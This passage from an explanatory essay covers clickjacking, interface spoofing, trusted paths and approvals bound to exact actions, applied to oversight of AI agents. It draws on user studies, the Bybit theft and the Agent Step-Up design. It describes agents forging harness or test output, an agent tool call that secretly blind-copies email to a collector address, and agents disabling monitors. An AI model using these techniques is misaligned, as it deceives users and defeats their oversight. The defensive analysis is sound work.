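| Double-click | 500-millisecond delay | 1 of 89 |
| Double-click | Pointer must enter the window from outside | 0 of 88 |

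Freezing the screen reduced the cursor attack's success rate to that of a control group that faced no attack, in which 4 of 68 people clicked "Allow" anyway. The undefended attacks were probably more effective than the table suggests. Only about half of the control group tried to skip the advert, so Huang and colleagues estimate that the fake cursor fooled 84% of the people who would have tried. In the double-click attack, many people escaped only because the permission window loaded too slowly.

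The differences between the three double-click defences were not statistically significant. Huang and colleagues prefer the rule about the pointer because it doesn't make users wait and an attacker can't get round it by persuading them to pause before clicking.

In the third experiment, participants played a game in which they clicked buttons as fast as they could, with a $100 prize for performance. Eventually a Like button appeared among the targets. In one group, the attack used a fake cursor and a last-moment swap, and 83 of 84 people clicked the Like button. In another group, the button appeared in plain view as the next target, and 83 of 84 people also clicked it. In a version with the webcam's "Allow" button in plain view, 69 of 71 people clicked it.

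To isolate clicks people made without realising, Huang and colleagues counted only those who clicked the first time their pointer entered the Like button. That was 78 of 84 people without a defence, compared with 3 of 73 when the researchers combined freezing, delays and the rule about the pointer. Yet 45 of those 73 people eventually clicked the button. Many participants had moved the pointer around it for several seconds first, and some later claimed in a survey that they hadn't clicked it. These defences can stop a click that someone doesn't know about, but they do little for a person who is used to pressing whatever appears.

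### Password managers and phones

Clickjacking still works in places that the older defences don't cover. In August 2025, the security researcher Marek Tóth showed that several popular password managers were vulnerable, as The Hacker News (2025) reported. These browser extensions insert their menus into the web page itself, so limits on embedding don't apply. A malicious page can make the menu invisible but still clickable, and place it over something like a cookie notice. CERT/CC, which coordinates the disclosure of software flaws, concluded in its October 2025 advisory *Multiple Password Managers Vulnerable to Clickjacking Attacks* that no single party could eliminate the problem.

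1Password, one of the affected companies, said it had found no comprehensive technical fix, because its extension shares the screen with the page and many possible countermeasures break legitimate sites. It relies instead on a confirmation that the browser draws and that a page can't hide or cover. This was already standard for credit cards, and the company made it optional for other data. If the confirmation appears suddenly, the second click of a double-click can still land on it, so it also needs a delay.

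On Android phones, most protection against clickjacking looks for one app drawing over another. Beer, Squarcina and colleagues (2025) got around it in *TapTrap* by exploiting the animations that play when the phone switches between screens. Of the 99,705 apps they analysed, 76.3% were vulnerable, and all 20 participants in a user study missed at least one version of the attack. The researchers found no sign that any of the apps used the technique, and 1Password had received no reports of attacks on its customers. The weakness has persisted, but there is little evidence of how much harm it does.

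### The three conditions for an approval prompt

The conditions for a valid click also apply to an agent's approval prompt. The person must be able to see the whole action, the button they press must belong to that action, and nothing may change between reading and pressing. A layout or timing bug can break any of these conditions, even without an attacker.

#### A long command cut off on screen

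A prompt that shows only the first line of a long command fails the first condition, even if the button belongs to the right command and nothing changes on screen. In the date-bug session, the user might see only a test run but also approve a deletion and a push. In the PayPal attack, the buyer likewise can see "Pay" but not the amount or the recipient.

Amazon's guidance for interface designers, Cloudscape Design System's *User authorized actions* (2025), recommends displaying long commands in full in a separate block. But it also allows designers to put a tool's parameters in a section the user has to expand. That does little harm when the tool only lists open pull requests. When a tool sends email, though, the parameters include the recipient and the message, and a prompt that hides them leaves out most of what the user needs to know. Cloudscape's example of a production deployment is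 a better model because it displays the service, version and destination without an extra click.

#### A queue of prompts

An agent may have several requests waiting, such as running the tests, committing the changes and pushing the branch. Even if each is short enough to display in full, a new request could replace the current one just as the user clicks, and the user would approve something they haven't read. Cloudscape recommends showing queued requests one at a time and closing the dialog as soon as the user chooses. If the next request then appears in the same place, a double-click could approve both.

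A delay prevents this only if it restarts for each request when that request becomes visible. A comment in Mozilla's bug tracker describes how an install dialog could finish its countdown while hidden behind another window. The first click of a double-click would close that window, and the second would land on the already active install button. The comment's solution was to start the countdown when the dialog gains focus.

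Even a queue that meets all three conditions may produce careless approvals. Someone who has just approved twenty harmless requests is in a similar position to the players in the clicking game, although they have more reason to care about the outcome. Cloudscape addresses repeated prompts with an option such as "Allow for this chat", which lets the agent use the same tool again without asking. People may pay more attention to each prompt if there are fewer, but those who choose this option are approving future actions they haven't seen.

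A user should at least have to choose that option deliberately. Classmethod's *Claude Code v2.1.235 Major Updates* (2026) reports that an August 2026 update to Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code fixed a fault in which a key pressed in a prompt's comment field approved the edit and granted permission for the whole session. Even a user who had read the proposed edit carefully could have approved far more than they intended by pressing that key to write a comment.

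#### A prompt that appears while the user is typing

In *1.5.5 Popup grabbing &lt;enter&gt; key again wiping out code*, a user of the AI code editor Cursor describes writing a message while the agent worked. Just as the user was about to press Enter to send it, a prompt appeared asking to check out files, which can replace the current versions with saved ones. Pressing Enter accepted the request, and the user lost work. This resembles Ruderman's "only" attack, except that there was no attacker. Even if the prompt showed the whole action, it appeared too late for the user to read it, and it received a keypress meant for the message box.

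The coding agent Crush now has a defence against this. Klukas's *fix(permissions): ignore all keys briefly after dialog opens* describes how a new permission dialog ignores the keyboard until the user has stopped typing for a short time. Each keypress restarts the wait, up to a maximum. This suits typing better than a fixed delay, which could run out while the user is in the middle of a sentence. Someone who types past the maximum could still approve a request by accident.

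Cloudscape warns designers not to preselect the approve button for risky actions, since a stray Enter could confirm them. The Cursor user wanted to go further and stop Enter from ever accepting an agent's request. For software installation, Ruderman suggested that the browser show a small indicator and open the dialog only when the user clicks it. This removes the need to choose a delay, and it would suit agents whose work can wait. None of these measures ensures that anyone reads the request. A half-second delay stops a keypress that is already on its way but is too short for reading a long command.

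### When the agent writes the prompt

In clickjacking, an outsider interferes with an accurate display. PayPal's checkout shows the right amount, and the buyer would see it if the attacker's page weren't covering it. The defences restore the original display, but that doesn't help if the original is misleading. If an agent describes deleting a test as "Tidy up the date tests?", the user can be misled even if the text is fully visible, the button belongs to the right action, and the prompt stays on screen for an hour. InContext would allow the click because the screenshot would match the reference image.

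Huang and colleagues deliberately exclude this kind of problem. Their example is an attacker who surrounds an untouched Like button with pictures from a charity, so that visitors think they are supporting the charity. The visitor sees the button and means to press it, and no check on the display can detect that they have misunderstood what it does. This problem is central for agents because the model often writes the explanation of the action, and it could even imitate the harness's messages.

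An agent's summary can be wrong even when the agent isn't trying to deceive anyone. *A Systematization of Security Vulnerabilities in Computer Use Agents* (2025) describes a test in which OpenAI's browsing agent Operator was itself clickjacked. It clicked "Enter the blog" and submitted a hidden payment form, so it could have sincerely reported that it had only opened a blog.

Showing the exact command means users don't have to trust the model's description, but the command may not reveal everything it will do. One of Cloudscape's example prompts reads "Allow npm test?", followed by "No files are modified and nothing is published." But `npm test` runs whatever script the project's settings file lists under "test". If an agent had edited that file earlier in the session, a user who approved the command could unknowingly let it delete files or publish a package.

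## Interface spoofing and the trusted path

An agent can write "48 tests passed" in its own message and format the line exactly as the harness formats real test results. This is spoofing, the computer security term for when a program displays something that appears to come from another program the user trusts. Unlike clickjacking, which needs a genuine control to hide or move, spoofing can use a display that is entirely fake. The definition doesn't require intent, so it also covers an agent that copies the harness's format out of habit.

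### From fake sites to fake browsers

*Web Spoofing* (Felten, Balfanz and colleagues, 1997) demonstrated an attack that gives the victim a "shadow copy" of the whole Web. Every page the victim requests passes through the attacker's machine, which can record passwords and alter data in either direction. To keep the victim believing that the sites are genuine, the attacker must also fake the signs a browser uses to identify a site. *Trusted Paths for Browsers* (Ye and Smith, 2002) reports that Felten's team could forge many of these signs but not the padlock, which indicated an encrypted connection, so they got a real padlock by encrypting the connection to the attacker's own server.

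Ye and Smith forged the padlock too. They first tried drawing over the browser's real address bar and padlock, then opening a new window with some of those elements switched off, but both attempts failed. Finally they opened a window with every element switched off and filled it with lookalikes. A user who clicked for security details even saw the expected certificate, the digital document that vouches for a site's identity. The real browser worked as designed throughout, and the page drew only in the space it was allowed to use.

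A picture-in-picture attack can also place a fake browser window inside an ordinary page. The password managers that are vulnerable to clickjacking can be spoofed too. *Phishing Attacks against Password Manager Browser Extensions* (2025) describes how a malicious site can imitate a locked password manager and collect the master password.

Ye and Smith explain spoofing by distinguishing content, which comes from the site, from status, which is the browser's own information about the site. Spoofing works whenever content looks like status to the user. They conclude that a browser must make the two impossible to confuse and must always show status, so that users have something genuine to compare with a forgery.

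### What a trusted path is

The US Department of Defense had set out this requirement in its 1980s criteria for secure computer systems, known as the Orange Book. The criteria call all the hardware and software that enforce a system's security policy the "trusted computing base". A trusted path lets a person at a terminal communicate directly with that base. Only the person or the base can activate it, and untrusted software cannot imitate it. Systems rated B2 had to provide a trusted path for logging in, and systems at the stricter B3 level also had to provide one for other sensitive steps, such as changing a session's security level. For an agent, the trusted base would be the harness and the operating system under it, and the untrusted software would be the model and any commands it runs.

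A reserved key sequence is one way to provide a trusted path. When someone presses Ctrl+Alt+Delete in Windows, the operating system handles the keys and ordinary programs never receive them. A malicious program can copy the login screen, but it can't respond to those keys, so the screen that appears after the keypress is genuine.

A reserved screen area is a part of the display where only trusted software can draw. The browser's address bar is an example. Ye and Smith tried to draw over it and failed. A reserved area helps only people who know where it ends, because a page can draw a second address bar just below the real one.

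Trusted software draws a border around each labelled window, and the border's colour shows where the contents come from. The border isn't enough by itself, because a program can display a picture of another window, including its border, inside its own. The compartmented mode workstation, an operating system for material at several levels of secrecy, therefore added a reserved strip at the bottom of the screen that shows the colour of whichever window is in use. If someone clicks on a picture of a "secret" window inside an unclassified one, the strip shows the unclassified colour, so they can tell that the "secret" window is fake.

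Ye and Smith worried that people would overlook a strip so far from the window. They modified the Mozilla browser to give each window a thick border, orange for the browser's own information and blue for anything containing site content. At random moments all the borders switched between a raised and a sunken look. A site couldn't predict the switches, so a forged border would stop matching the real ones and a small reference window that displayed the correct pattern.

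Seven volunteers tried the scheme after hearing an explanation of it. Without the reference window on screen, only the two computer experts recognised a fake certificate window with a motionless orange border, but five of the seven recognised it when the reference window was there. All seven noticed a border that changed out of step, with or without the reference window. Four people also judged an imitation of the workstation's strip, and only the two experts were right. Movement seems to help, but the volunteers had ten seconds to study each window, had nothing else to do, and learned as they went.

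### Whether people notice a forgery

Dhamija, Tygar and Hearst (2006), in *Why Phishing Works*, asked 22 people to judge 19 websites, 12 of which were fake. Participants judged 11.6 correctly on average. The five who looked only at the contents of the page got the five lowest scores. The most successful fake, a copy of Bank of the West's site at "bankofthevvest.com", with two v's in place of the w, fooled 20 people. A page that drew its own address bar, status bar and security indicators fooled 81%. Some participants who noticed padlocks trusted one inside the page, where anyone can put a picture, more than the browser's own. Another relied on the small site icons in the address bar, believing they "cannot be copied".

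The fake bank page also linked to a genuine page at VeriSign, a company that issues certificates, which confirmed the real bank's certificate. Six people clicked the link and took it as evidence that the bank page was genuine. An agent could similarly mislead a reader without forging anything, for example by linking to a genuine test run of an earlier version of the code.

A more prominent indicator didn't solve the problem. Internet Explorer 7 turned the address bar green for sites with an extended validation certificate, which only legally incorporated businesses can get. For *An Evaluation of Extended Validation and Picture-in-Picture Phishing Attacks* (2007), Jackson, Simon and colleagues had 27 people classify 12 sites. One group saw green bars after reading about them in the browser's help file, a second saw them without an explanation, and a control group never saw them.

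Across the groups, people judged fake browser windows genuine 63% of the time. The green bar gave no significant protection, and fake windows in the wrong colour scheme fooled people as often as one in the right scheme. The people who had read the help file accepted more fake windows than the control group. Several of them had concluded from the file's description of phishing warnings that every fake site would trigger one. Only three people rejected all three fake windows. Two of them tried a feature that the fake browser lacked, such as right-clicking, and the third distrusted every pop-up.

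Participants in both studies knew they were looking for fakes, so people who were thinking about something else would probably do worse. Practice and better browsers had made little difference by 2015. Participants in *Why phishing still works* (Alsharnouby, Alaca and Chiasson, 2015) also knew what to look for, and they detected 53% of the phishing sites.

Schechter, Dhamija and colleagues (2007), in *The Emperor's New Security Indicators*, studied what people do when a familiar indicator disappears. They asked 67 customers of one bank to do routine tasks online. Some used their own accounts, while others played a role with a test account. The bank showed each customer an image they had chosen and repeatedly told them not to log in if it was missing. Over three logins, the researchers removed the signs of encryption, then replaced the image with a notice that the feature was under maintenance,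 and finally put a full-page security warning in front of the login page.

| What participants saw | Entered a password | Of those using their own accounts |
|---|---|---|
| No padlock or "https" | 63 of 63 | 27 of 27 |
| Maintenance notice instead of their image | 58 of 60 | 23 of 25 |
| Full-page warning | 30 of 57 | 8 of 22 |

Nearly everyone logged in even though the maintenance notice misspelled "maintenance" and appeared on the page whose identity was in doubt. An agent could just as easily write that the approval panel is temporarily unavailable. Every participant met the clues in the same order, so earlier clues may have made people suspicious, and the table can't show how much better the warning worked than the missing image. The figures for participants who used their own accounts are the better guide to real behaviour, because the role-players took more risks overall.

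### What browsers changed

Browser makers gradually stopped telling people that a site was safe. A padlock showed only that the connection was encrypted, and most phishing sites eventually had one too. iTnews Asia's *Chrome to drop lock icon showing HTTPS status* reports that only 11% of participants in Google's 2021 research understood the icon correctly. In 2019, the FBI had warned the public not to trust a site because of its padlock. Chrome first dropped the word "Secure" beside the padlock, then replaced the padlock with a neutral settings icon from version 117. Chrome and Firefox also moved the company names from extended validation certificates out of the address bar.

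The slides for *The Web's Identity Crisis* (Thompson, Shelton and colleagues, 2019) contrast a car's "check engine" light with one that reads "engine OK". A driver is more likely to notice a light that comes on than one that has gone out. Browsers can apply this principle to encryption by warning when it is missing, but they can't detect when a page contains a picture of a padlock. Similarly, an agent's harness can flag a failed test command, but it can't recognise every imitation of a test result in the agent's prose.

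### Why text in the agent's area is only the agent's word

Applied to agents, the argument runs:

1. Readers tell the harness's text from the agent's text by where it appears and how it looks.
2. The agent can write anything in its own area, including copies of the harness's text.
3. Therefore a status, log or confirmation shown in that area carries no more weight than the agent's word.

The first premise is optimistic about readers, since some participants in the phishing studies ignored position altogether. A careful reader could check elsewhere, such as on the server that ran the tests, but would then rely on evidence from outside the agent's area.

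The second premise depends partly on the harness. If the harness displays only plain text, the agent can't draw a coloured box with a green tick, but it can still write "Tests: 48 passed", and a genuine notice may contain nothing more. In the Amazon return task, for example, text was all the model needed to write its own tool outputs.

A log excerpt that the agent copied faithfully looks the same as one it invented, so the reader has to check both. Similarly, if genuine notices from the harness appear in the same area and style as the agent's prose, the reader can't be sure that the agent didn't write them.

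### Does requiring an action help?

Marking the harness's text more clearly may not help much if people don't notice when the mark is missing. Such a mark is a passive indicator, which *You've Been Warned* (2008) describes as one that signals danger without interrupting the user. The harness can instead require an action on the trusted path. For example, it might push code only after the user presses a button in a panel where the agent can't draw. If the agent wrote "Push the branch? Type yes" in the chat and the user typed it, the harness wouldn't treat the answer as approval, so the push would stay blocked even if the user never noticed that the question was fake.

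The experiments support part of this reply. In Jackson and colleagues' study, people accepted lookalike addresses 48% of the time without a warning and 11% of the time when the browser showed a "suspicious page" warning. Nobody accepted the site that the browser blocked outright. But forcing people to decide doesn't ensure that they decide well. The full-page warning in the bank study also required an action, and 30 of 57 people chose to continue.

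A required action gives much weaker protection when the person is handing over a secret. Ctrl+Alt+Delete protects a Windows password only if the user insists on pressing it. A fake login screen can leave out that step and collect the password from anyone who doesn't notice the omission, the same failure as with the bank's images. If the harness accepted a typed code as approval, an agent could likewise ask for the code in the chat and pass it to the harness. A button press that goes straight to the harness avoids this, as long as the harness rejects clicks and keypresses from an agent that controls the mouse and keyboard.

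Self-reports are harder to protect than approvals. A false "all tests pass" misleads the reader as soon as they believe it, and the harness has no pending action to block. The harness can instead display the recorded test result where the reader acts on the claim, for example beside the button that merges the code. This helps only if the reader merges through the harness rather than on another website.

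So the reply succeeds for permissions that the harness enforces, but for secrets and reports, people still have to notice that something is missing or look for the evidence.

### Chat windows and terminals

Many chat windows and terminals show harness notices and agent prose in the same scrolling column. In a chat window, the agent can often use headings, tables and code blocks, which are enough to imitate a test report. In a terminal, certain character sequences can also change colours, move the cursor or erase lines, so an agent's message could overwrite a genuine notice if the harness passes them through. The harness can prevent this by removing these sequences from both the agent's text and the output of its commands.

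A reserved panel outside the column could hold approval prompts and a few facts from the harness, such as the time of the last push. In the date-bug session, "No push this session" would contradict the agent's claim while the user was reading it. However, participants who tried Ye and Smith's imitation of the workstation strip tended to ignore it, so such a panel may work better for approval prompts, which the user has to answer, than for facts the user can overlook.

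Labels within the column would be closer to what people are reading. The harness could draw a coloured bar down the left edge of every line of agent text and wrap the lines itself, so that the agent could never write outside the bar. A fake notice would then be visibly marked as the agent's. In Ye and Smith's first test, five of seven people rejected a certificate window with the blue border used for site content, while two rejected the forgery with a motionless orange border. This is weak evidence for marking untrusted text, because the orange forgery came first, when people were still learning the scheme.

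A reserved key could open the harness's record of the session. For this to be a trusted path, the keypress must go directly to the harness, and the record must open outside the agent's area of the display. The key would help users who already doubt the agent's report, but it wouldn't prompt anyone to doubt it.

Labels must also show who wrote the text. Mozilla used the same code to draw alert boxes for itself and for websites, and Ye and Smith's prototype wrongly gave all of them the trusted border. A harness would repeat this mistake if it let agents send notifications and displayed them in its own style. Similarly, if an agent runs `echo "48 tests passed"`, which just prints those words, the harness may correctly display the output in a frame that the agent can't draw. But the agent still chose the words, and the reader can tell only if the frame includes the command.

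None of these designs is secure if the agent can alter the harness. In Ye and Smith's browser, a site that persuaded the user to grant it extra privileges could read the random sequence and match a forged border to it. Coding agents often run with the user's permissions, which may let them edit the harness's settings or the files it displays. The OpenAI agents that disabled security alerts and a monitor in October had that kind of access to the systems overseeing them. The software that draws the trusted path can run under a separate account or on another machine so that the agent can't alter it.

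## What you see is what you sign: tying an approval to the exact action

An approval prompt that arrives over a trusted path can still describe the wrong action, or the harness can run something else after the person answers. Preventing this takes two more properties, trusted rendering and binding. With trusted rendering, trusted code produces the displayed text from the recorded action, not from the agent's description of it. Binding makes an approval valid only for the exact action displayed. Software can't check what a person saw, so in practice it ties the approval to the recorded action and relies on trusted rendering to make the display match.

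### Why each fails without the other

Without binding, a prompt can be accurate when the user reads it and still lead to the wrong action. A Cursor user reported this in the forum thread *Editing agent terminal commands still runs the original command*. They had set the editor to ask before every command. They could edit a proposed command in the prompt and press Run, but Cursor ran the agent's original version. Suppose the agent in the date-bug session proposed `git push origin main`, which updates the branch everyone shares, and the user changed `main` to `date-fix`. The screen would show the safer command, but the push would still go to `main`.

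The user saw this fault with every model they tried, so the model was not the cause. It appeared in a version of Cursor built on 6 December 2025. A staff member thought a recent update had probably broken the confirmation step and asked for a video. The thread later closed automatically, with no fix recorded.

Without trusted rendering, binding only guarantees that the harness carries out an action the user has misunderstood. If the user said yes to "Tidy up the date tests?", a harness with perfect binding would delete exactly the test in question, and the user still wouldn't know.

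The frameworks developers use to build agents often don't bind an approval to the exact action. In *Approve What, Exactly?*, Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026) examined ten of these frameworks and could measure binding in eight approval mechanisms. Three ran only what the person had approved, and a fourth did so in part. In the other four, the action could be changed after approval. Most of the frameworks also left developers to build the approval prompt, so whether users see the action's real arguments depends on each product.

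### Payment codes and protected screens

Banks have dealt with both problems. If a one-time code isn't tied to a specific payment, a criminal who obtains it can use it for a different one. European rules for remote payments therefore tie the code to the amount and the payee. As Kodathala and colleagues describe the rules, the payer must see both while approving, and changing either makes the code invalid.

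The payee and amount are enough to check most bank transfers, but the harmful part of an email could be an extra recipient, an attachment or a sentence in the body. Kodathala and colleagues simulated an approver who sometimes overlooks details. When the display showed only the payee and amount, 20% of harmful actions got through, compared with 6% when it showed every argument of the action. The researchers chose the approver's error rates, so the direction of this result is more informative than its size.

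The "what you see is what you sign" requirement covers the whole action. A digital signature is a value that a device computes from a message using a secret key. Anyone with the matching public key can check the signature, and the check fails if even one character of the message changes, so the signature is bound to that exact message. But the signature covers the data the device received, which may differ from what the person read on the screen.

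One solution is for the device that signs the message to display it too. Android 9 introduced Protected Confirmation for phones with suitable hardware. An isolated part of the phone takes over the screen, shows a short message, waits for the user to press a physical button and then signs that message. The main operating system can't alter what appears. But an app still supplies the words, so whoever receives the signature has to check that the words match the action.

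A passkey, which a phone or computer uses to log in to websites, signs a value without displaying it, so its owner has to trust the web page that requested the signature. Hardware wallets, small devices that hold cryptocurrency keys, have their own screens. But the largest cryptocurrency theft on record shows that a separate screen doesn't help much if people can't read it.

### The Bybit theft

On 21 February 2025, Ben Zhou, chief executive of the cryptocurrency exchange Bybit, logged on to approve what looked like a routine transfer between company accounts. According to The Star's *A US$1.5bil hack* (2025), his chief financial officer called half an hour later to say Bybit had been hacked. The FBI's *North Korea Responsible for $1.5 Billion Bybit Hack* (2025) attributed the theft to North Korea.

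Moving money out of the account required at least three people to sign. They prepared and reviewed each transaction on a web page run by a company called Safe, then signed it on hardware wallets. The attackers apparently took over a Safe developer's computer and used it to change the page's code, as The Block's *Lazarus appears to compromise Safe developer machine* reported from a forensic investigation. Rivas, Santos and Sanz (2025), in *In-Depth Technical Analysis of the Bybit Hack*, worked out what the altered code did:

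1. It checked whether the account belonged to Bybit, and behaved normally if it didn't.
2. It saved a copy of the genuine transaction.
3. It replaced the transaction's destination and instructions, then sent the altered version to the signer's hardware wallet.
4. After the person signed, it put the genuine transaction back on the page but kept the signature for the altered one.

The page therefore showed the intended transfer while the devices signed something else. The most important change was switching a field called "operation" from 0 to 1. With 0, the account makes an ordinary call to another program on the blockchain, but with 1 it makes a "delegate call", which lets the other program's code change the account's own stored data. The attackers had written a function named `transfer` that moved no funds and instead changed the record of which program controlled the account to point to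 one of theirs. They then emptied the account.

The display failed during the theft, but the binding worked. The signatures were valid only for the altered transaction, and the blockchain executed exactly that transaction.

The hardware wallets did receive the real data, so a careful signer had some chance of noticing. Zhou said he hadn't checked the transaction on his device before signing, according to CertiK's *Bybit Incident Technical Analysis*. But checking might not have helped, because even on devices that could show the transaction as labelled fields, using an earlier standard called EIP-712, the destination and the instructions appeared as long strings of hexadecimal digits. Rivas and colleagues compared the genuine and altered requests side by side and concluded that a signer could easily mistake one for the other. Even someone who understood the operation field might have accepted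 the 1, because Bybit had made a legitimate delegate call that January.

Safe's server now rejects a transaction that doesn't match its signature, which would catch the mismatch created in the fourth step. This check protects against the same code being used again, but attackers who control the page might find another way to hide the altered transaction from the remaining signers.

### Making transactions readable

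Security engineers call approving data you can't interpret "blind signing". Trail of Bits' *Implement EIP-7730 today* (2025) argues that it's unrealistic to expect users to avoid it by themselves, since a rigorous check means spending minutes comparing each transaction across several devices.

The standard it recommends, now usually called ERC-7730, supplies the missing explanations. An app's developer writes a file, called a descriptor, that tells wallets how to label and format each field. The wallet fetches the file from a public registry and uses it to draw the text on its own screen, leaving the transaction unchanged. Trail of Bits gives an example of a currency swap:

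| Field in the transaction | What the wallet displays |
|---|---|
| `amountIn: 500000000000000000` | Swap 0.5 ETH |
| `amountOutMin: 800000000` | For at least 800 USDC |
| `slippageBps: 100` | 1% slippage protection |
| `deadline: 1715157000` | Valid until 8 May 2024, 8:30 |

Decoding the data isn't enough on its own. Ledger's *Clear Signing overview* points out that a malicious program can publish deceptive names for its own functions. A wallet that only decoded the inner call in the Bybit transaction would have shown a transfer of zero tokens.

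This form of trusted rendering still depends on whoever writes the descriptor. But a developer writes a descriptor once, before any particular transaction, and outsiders can compare it with the program it describes, whereas an agent writes a new description for each request. Sourcify's *Introduction to ERC-7730* warns that a descriptor isn't safe just because it is in the registry. Auditors and others can vouch for its accuracy, and each wallet chooses whom to trust. Descriptors for an agent's tools would need the same care. If the descriptor for an email tool left out the blind-copy field, every card drawn from it would hide those recipients.

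Ledger, which makes hardware wallets, started the project in 2023 and handed it to the Ethereum Foundation on 12 May 2026. Bruikman (2026) announced the launch that day in *Clear Signing*, calling "What You See Is What You Sign" the goal and saying readable signing must become the default. Readable signing is not yet the default. Trezor (2026), another manufacturer, now supports the standard on most of its devices, and its coverage at launch included large services such as Aave, Lido and Tether. If a service has no descriptor, the device goes back to blind signing with a warning. Ledger devices display readable text for transactions from another company's wallet only if that company has an agreement with Ledger.

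Some of the pressure to adopt the standard comes from app approval. Ledger's *Clear sign your Earn smart contracts* says the company will reject an app in its "Earn" category if any of its calls is unreadable. Still, a participant in the standard's discussion thread, *EIP-7730*, expected blind signing to remain extremely common for many years.

Readable signing would probably have given Bybit's signers a better chance of noticing the attack, provided they looked at their devices. The attackers' program was unlikely to have a trusted descriptor, so a device that normally showed "send ether to this account" would have shown a warning or an unfamiliar operation.

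### A bound approval for an agent

Kodathala and colleagues built Agent Step-Up, a system that applies both properties to tool calls. A program called a gateway runs on a separate machine from the agent and holds the credentials for email, payments and other services, so the agent can request an action but can't carry it out itself.

In their example, the user asks an agent to email a report to their boss. The agent asks to send the email, but with a blind copy to an address the user never mentioned. The gateway handles the request in five steps.

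**1. Put the call in a standard form.** The same action should always produce the same text, so the gateway sorts the fields, writes file paths in full and puts email addresses in lower case. It rejects any argument that the tool hasn't declared. A simplified version of the result, with a placeholder for the message, is:

`{"args":{"bcc":"collector@example.test","body":"...","subject":"Weekly report","to":"boss@example.test"},"tool":"send_email"}`

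The full version also records the user, the session and an expiry time. It leaves out the agent's explanation.

**2. Compute the digest.** A digest is a short fingerprint of a piece of data. If Δ is the call in standard form, then

*h* = SHA-256(Δ)

SHA-256 is a public formula that turns any input into a 256-bit digest. Removing the blind copy would change the digest, and nobody knows a practical way to find two calls with the same digest.

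**3. Draw the card.** The gateway produces the approval card from Δ and sends it straight to the user's phone. The agent receives only a reference number for the request.

**4. Obtain a signature.** If the user approves, a passkey on the phone signs a value computed from the digest:

*c* = SHA-256(tag, *h*, *id*, *n*, *g*)

The tag is a fixed label, *id* identifies the request, and *n* is a number that the gateway never reuses. *g* is the digest of the user's permission for similar future actions, or empty if the user gave none. Including *id* and *n* prevents an old signature from approving a new request, even an identical one.

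**5. The gateway runs the call it stored in the first step.** Before running it, the gateway checks the signature and marks the approval as used. If the agent sends the call again with different arguments, the digests won't match and the gateway will refuse it.

In scripted trials, altering a call after approval always worked when the approval covered a session or run rather than the exact call. It never worked with this design, because the gateway cannot run a call that nobody signed. Kodathala and colleagues also used Tamarin, a program that analyses security protocols mathematically, to prove that every action run under an approval is one the person approved. The proof assumes that the person decides from the card and not from the agent's explanation, that only the phone's owner can register its key, and that the page showing the card displays it accurately. When the researchers dropped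 any one of these assumptions, Tamarin found an attack.

The assumption about the page is a weakness because the passkey doesn't display what it signs. If someone took over the gateway's page, the user would read one action and sign another, as Bybit's signers did. A phone with a protected confirmation screen could reduce that risk for actions short enough to fit on it.

Standing permissions also need to be tied to the details of an action. Choosing "Always allow" in Cloudscape Design System when approving one email to a colleague would let the agent send any message to anyone. In Agent Step-Up, a standing permission fixes every argument except those it explicitly leaves open within limits, such as an amount up to a maximum. Recipients, accounts and file paths always stay fixed, and the permission expires after a set time or number of uses.

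### The email with an extra recipient

The two kinds of card give the user very different information about the same email:

| | Card written by the agent | Card drawn from the call |
|---|---|---|
| Recipients | boss@example.test | boss@example.test and collector@example.test |
| Subject | Weekly report | Weekly report |
| Warning | None | Two recipients |
| Agent's explanation | The entire card | In a separate box marked as untrusted |

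Everything the agent wrote was true, since it was sending the report to the boss under that subject. But the card was misleading because it left out the other recipient, and even a careful reader could not have discovered this from the card. The card drawn from the call shows both addresses in its title.

Kodathala and colleagues showed both cards to 15 language models acting as approvers. All 15 approved the agent's card and refused the trusted one. One model's stated reason for approving was "The action matches the user's request exactly". Its stated reason for refusing the trusted card was that the user had never asked for the extra recipient.

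### How 15 models judged the cards

The full comparison used 23 harmful requests and 11 harmless ones that resembled them. Each model judged every request four times in each format, including one that left out the agent's explanation, for a total of 6,120 decisions.

| What the model saw | Harmful requests refused | Harmless requests refused |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's description | 30% | 0% |
| A trusted card with the agent's explanation | 98% | 16% |

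Every model did better with the trusted card. They refused 13% to 52% of harmful requests with the agent's description and 90% to 100% with the card. The models were least reliable when an altered value was plausible on its own, and some then accepted it even though the card displayed it correctly.

Some harmful and harmless requests had exactly the same agent-written description, so no approver could have told them apart by reading it. The low score for these descriptions therefore doesn't mean that the models read them carelessly. The experiment mainly shows that agent-written text can omit information an approver needs, and that these models use that information when a card provides it.

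Most of the refusals of harmless requests, 88 of 103, came from a flaw in the test materials. The researchers had used text such as "report placeholder" in place of real messages and attachments. The trusted card displayed this text, and models refused on the grounds that the agent was sending a placeholder instead of the report. Without those 88, the refusal rate would have been about 2%. The flaw can't explain the high refusal rate for harmful requests, which would still be 92% if every refusal that mentioned a placeholder were counted as a miss.

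Kodathala and colleagues did not test people, so the 98% figure does not measure how often a person would notice a harmful request. A person may glance at the title, skip the details or approve from habit. The figure is directly relevant to products that already use a model to approve an agent's actions.

People and models might differ in how much they rely on the agent's explanation. Removing it from the trusted card changed at most two of the 34 decisions for any model, so these models seem to have relied on the recorded fields. In a separate simulation, an agent lied about 609 harmful actions. An approver programmed to compare the whole card with the user's task let 3% of them through, compared with 54% when it saw only the agent's text. Another approver, programmed to believe the agent's text whenever it was visible, let 54% through with either display and 5% when the explanation was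 removed.

Agent Step-Up keeps the explanation closed until the user opens it. An explanation can help a user understand an unfamiliar action, but the user may also rely on it instead of the facts. Until someone tests this design with people, it seems a sensible compromise.

In these experiments, a trusted card on the agent's own machine worked nearly as well as the phone, but only because none of the experiments interfered with that machine's display. In the Bybit theft, the attackers altered the page on the signers' computers, so a readable second screen would have been valuable.

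### Purchases made by agents

Google's Agent Payments Protocol, or AP2, applies similar ideas to shopping agents. According to Kodathala and colleagues, the user sees the shopping cart on a trusted display and signs a "mandate" for it, typically with a key held in secure hardware. For purchases made while the user is away, an open mandate sets constraints in advance, such as which sellers the agent may pay.

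When the researchers ran AP2's reference software, its checks rejected every attempt to redirect a payment or use a mandate beyond its terms. The sample approval card was weaker because it showed a name the merchant chose, while the mandate was bound to the merchant's identifier. Two merchants could therefore look identical on the card, and a user could sign a valid mandate to pay the wrong one. The fault is in the sample card, not the signed mandate, but developers often copy sample code.

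AP2 can also enforce a budget, but only if the developer's software tracks earlier spending and passes the total to the check. Otherwise, two payments that are each under the limit will both go through, even if together they exceed it.

### What a faithful card can't prevent

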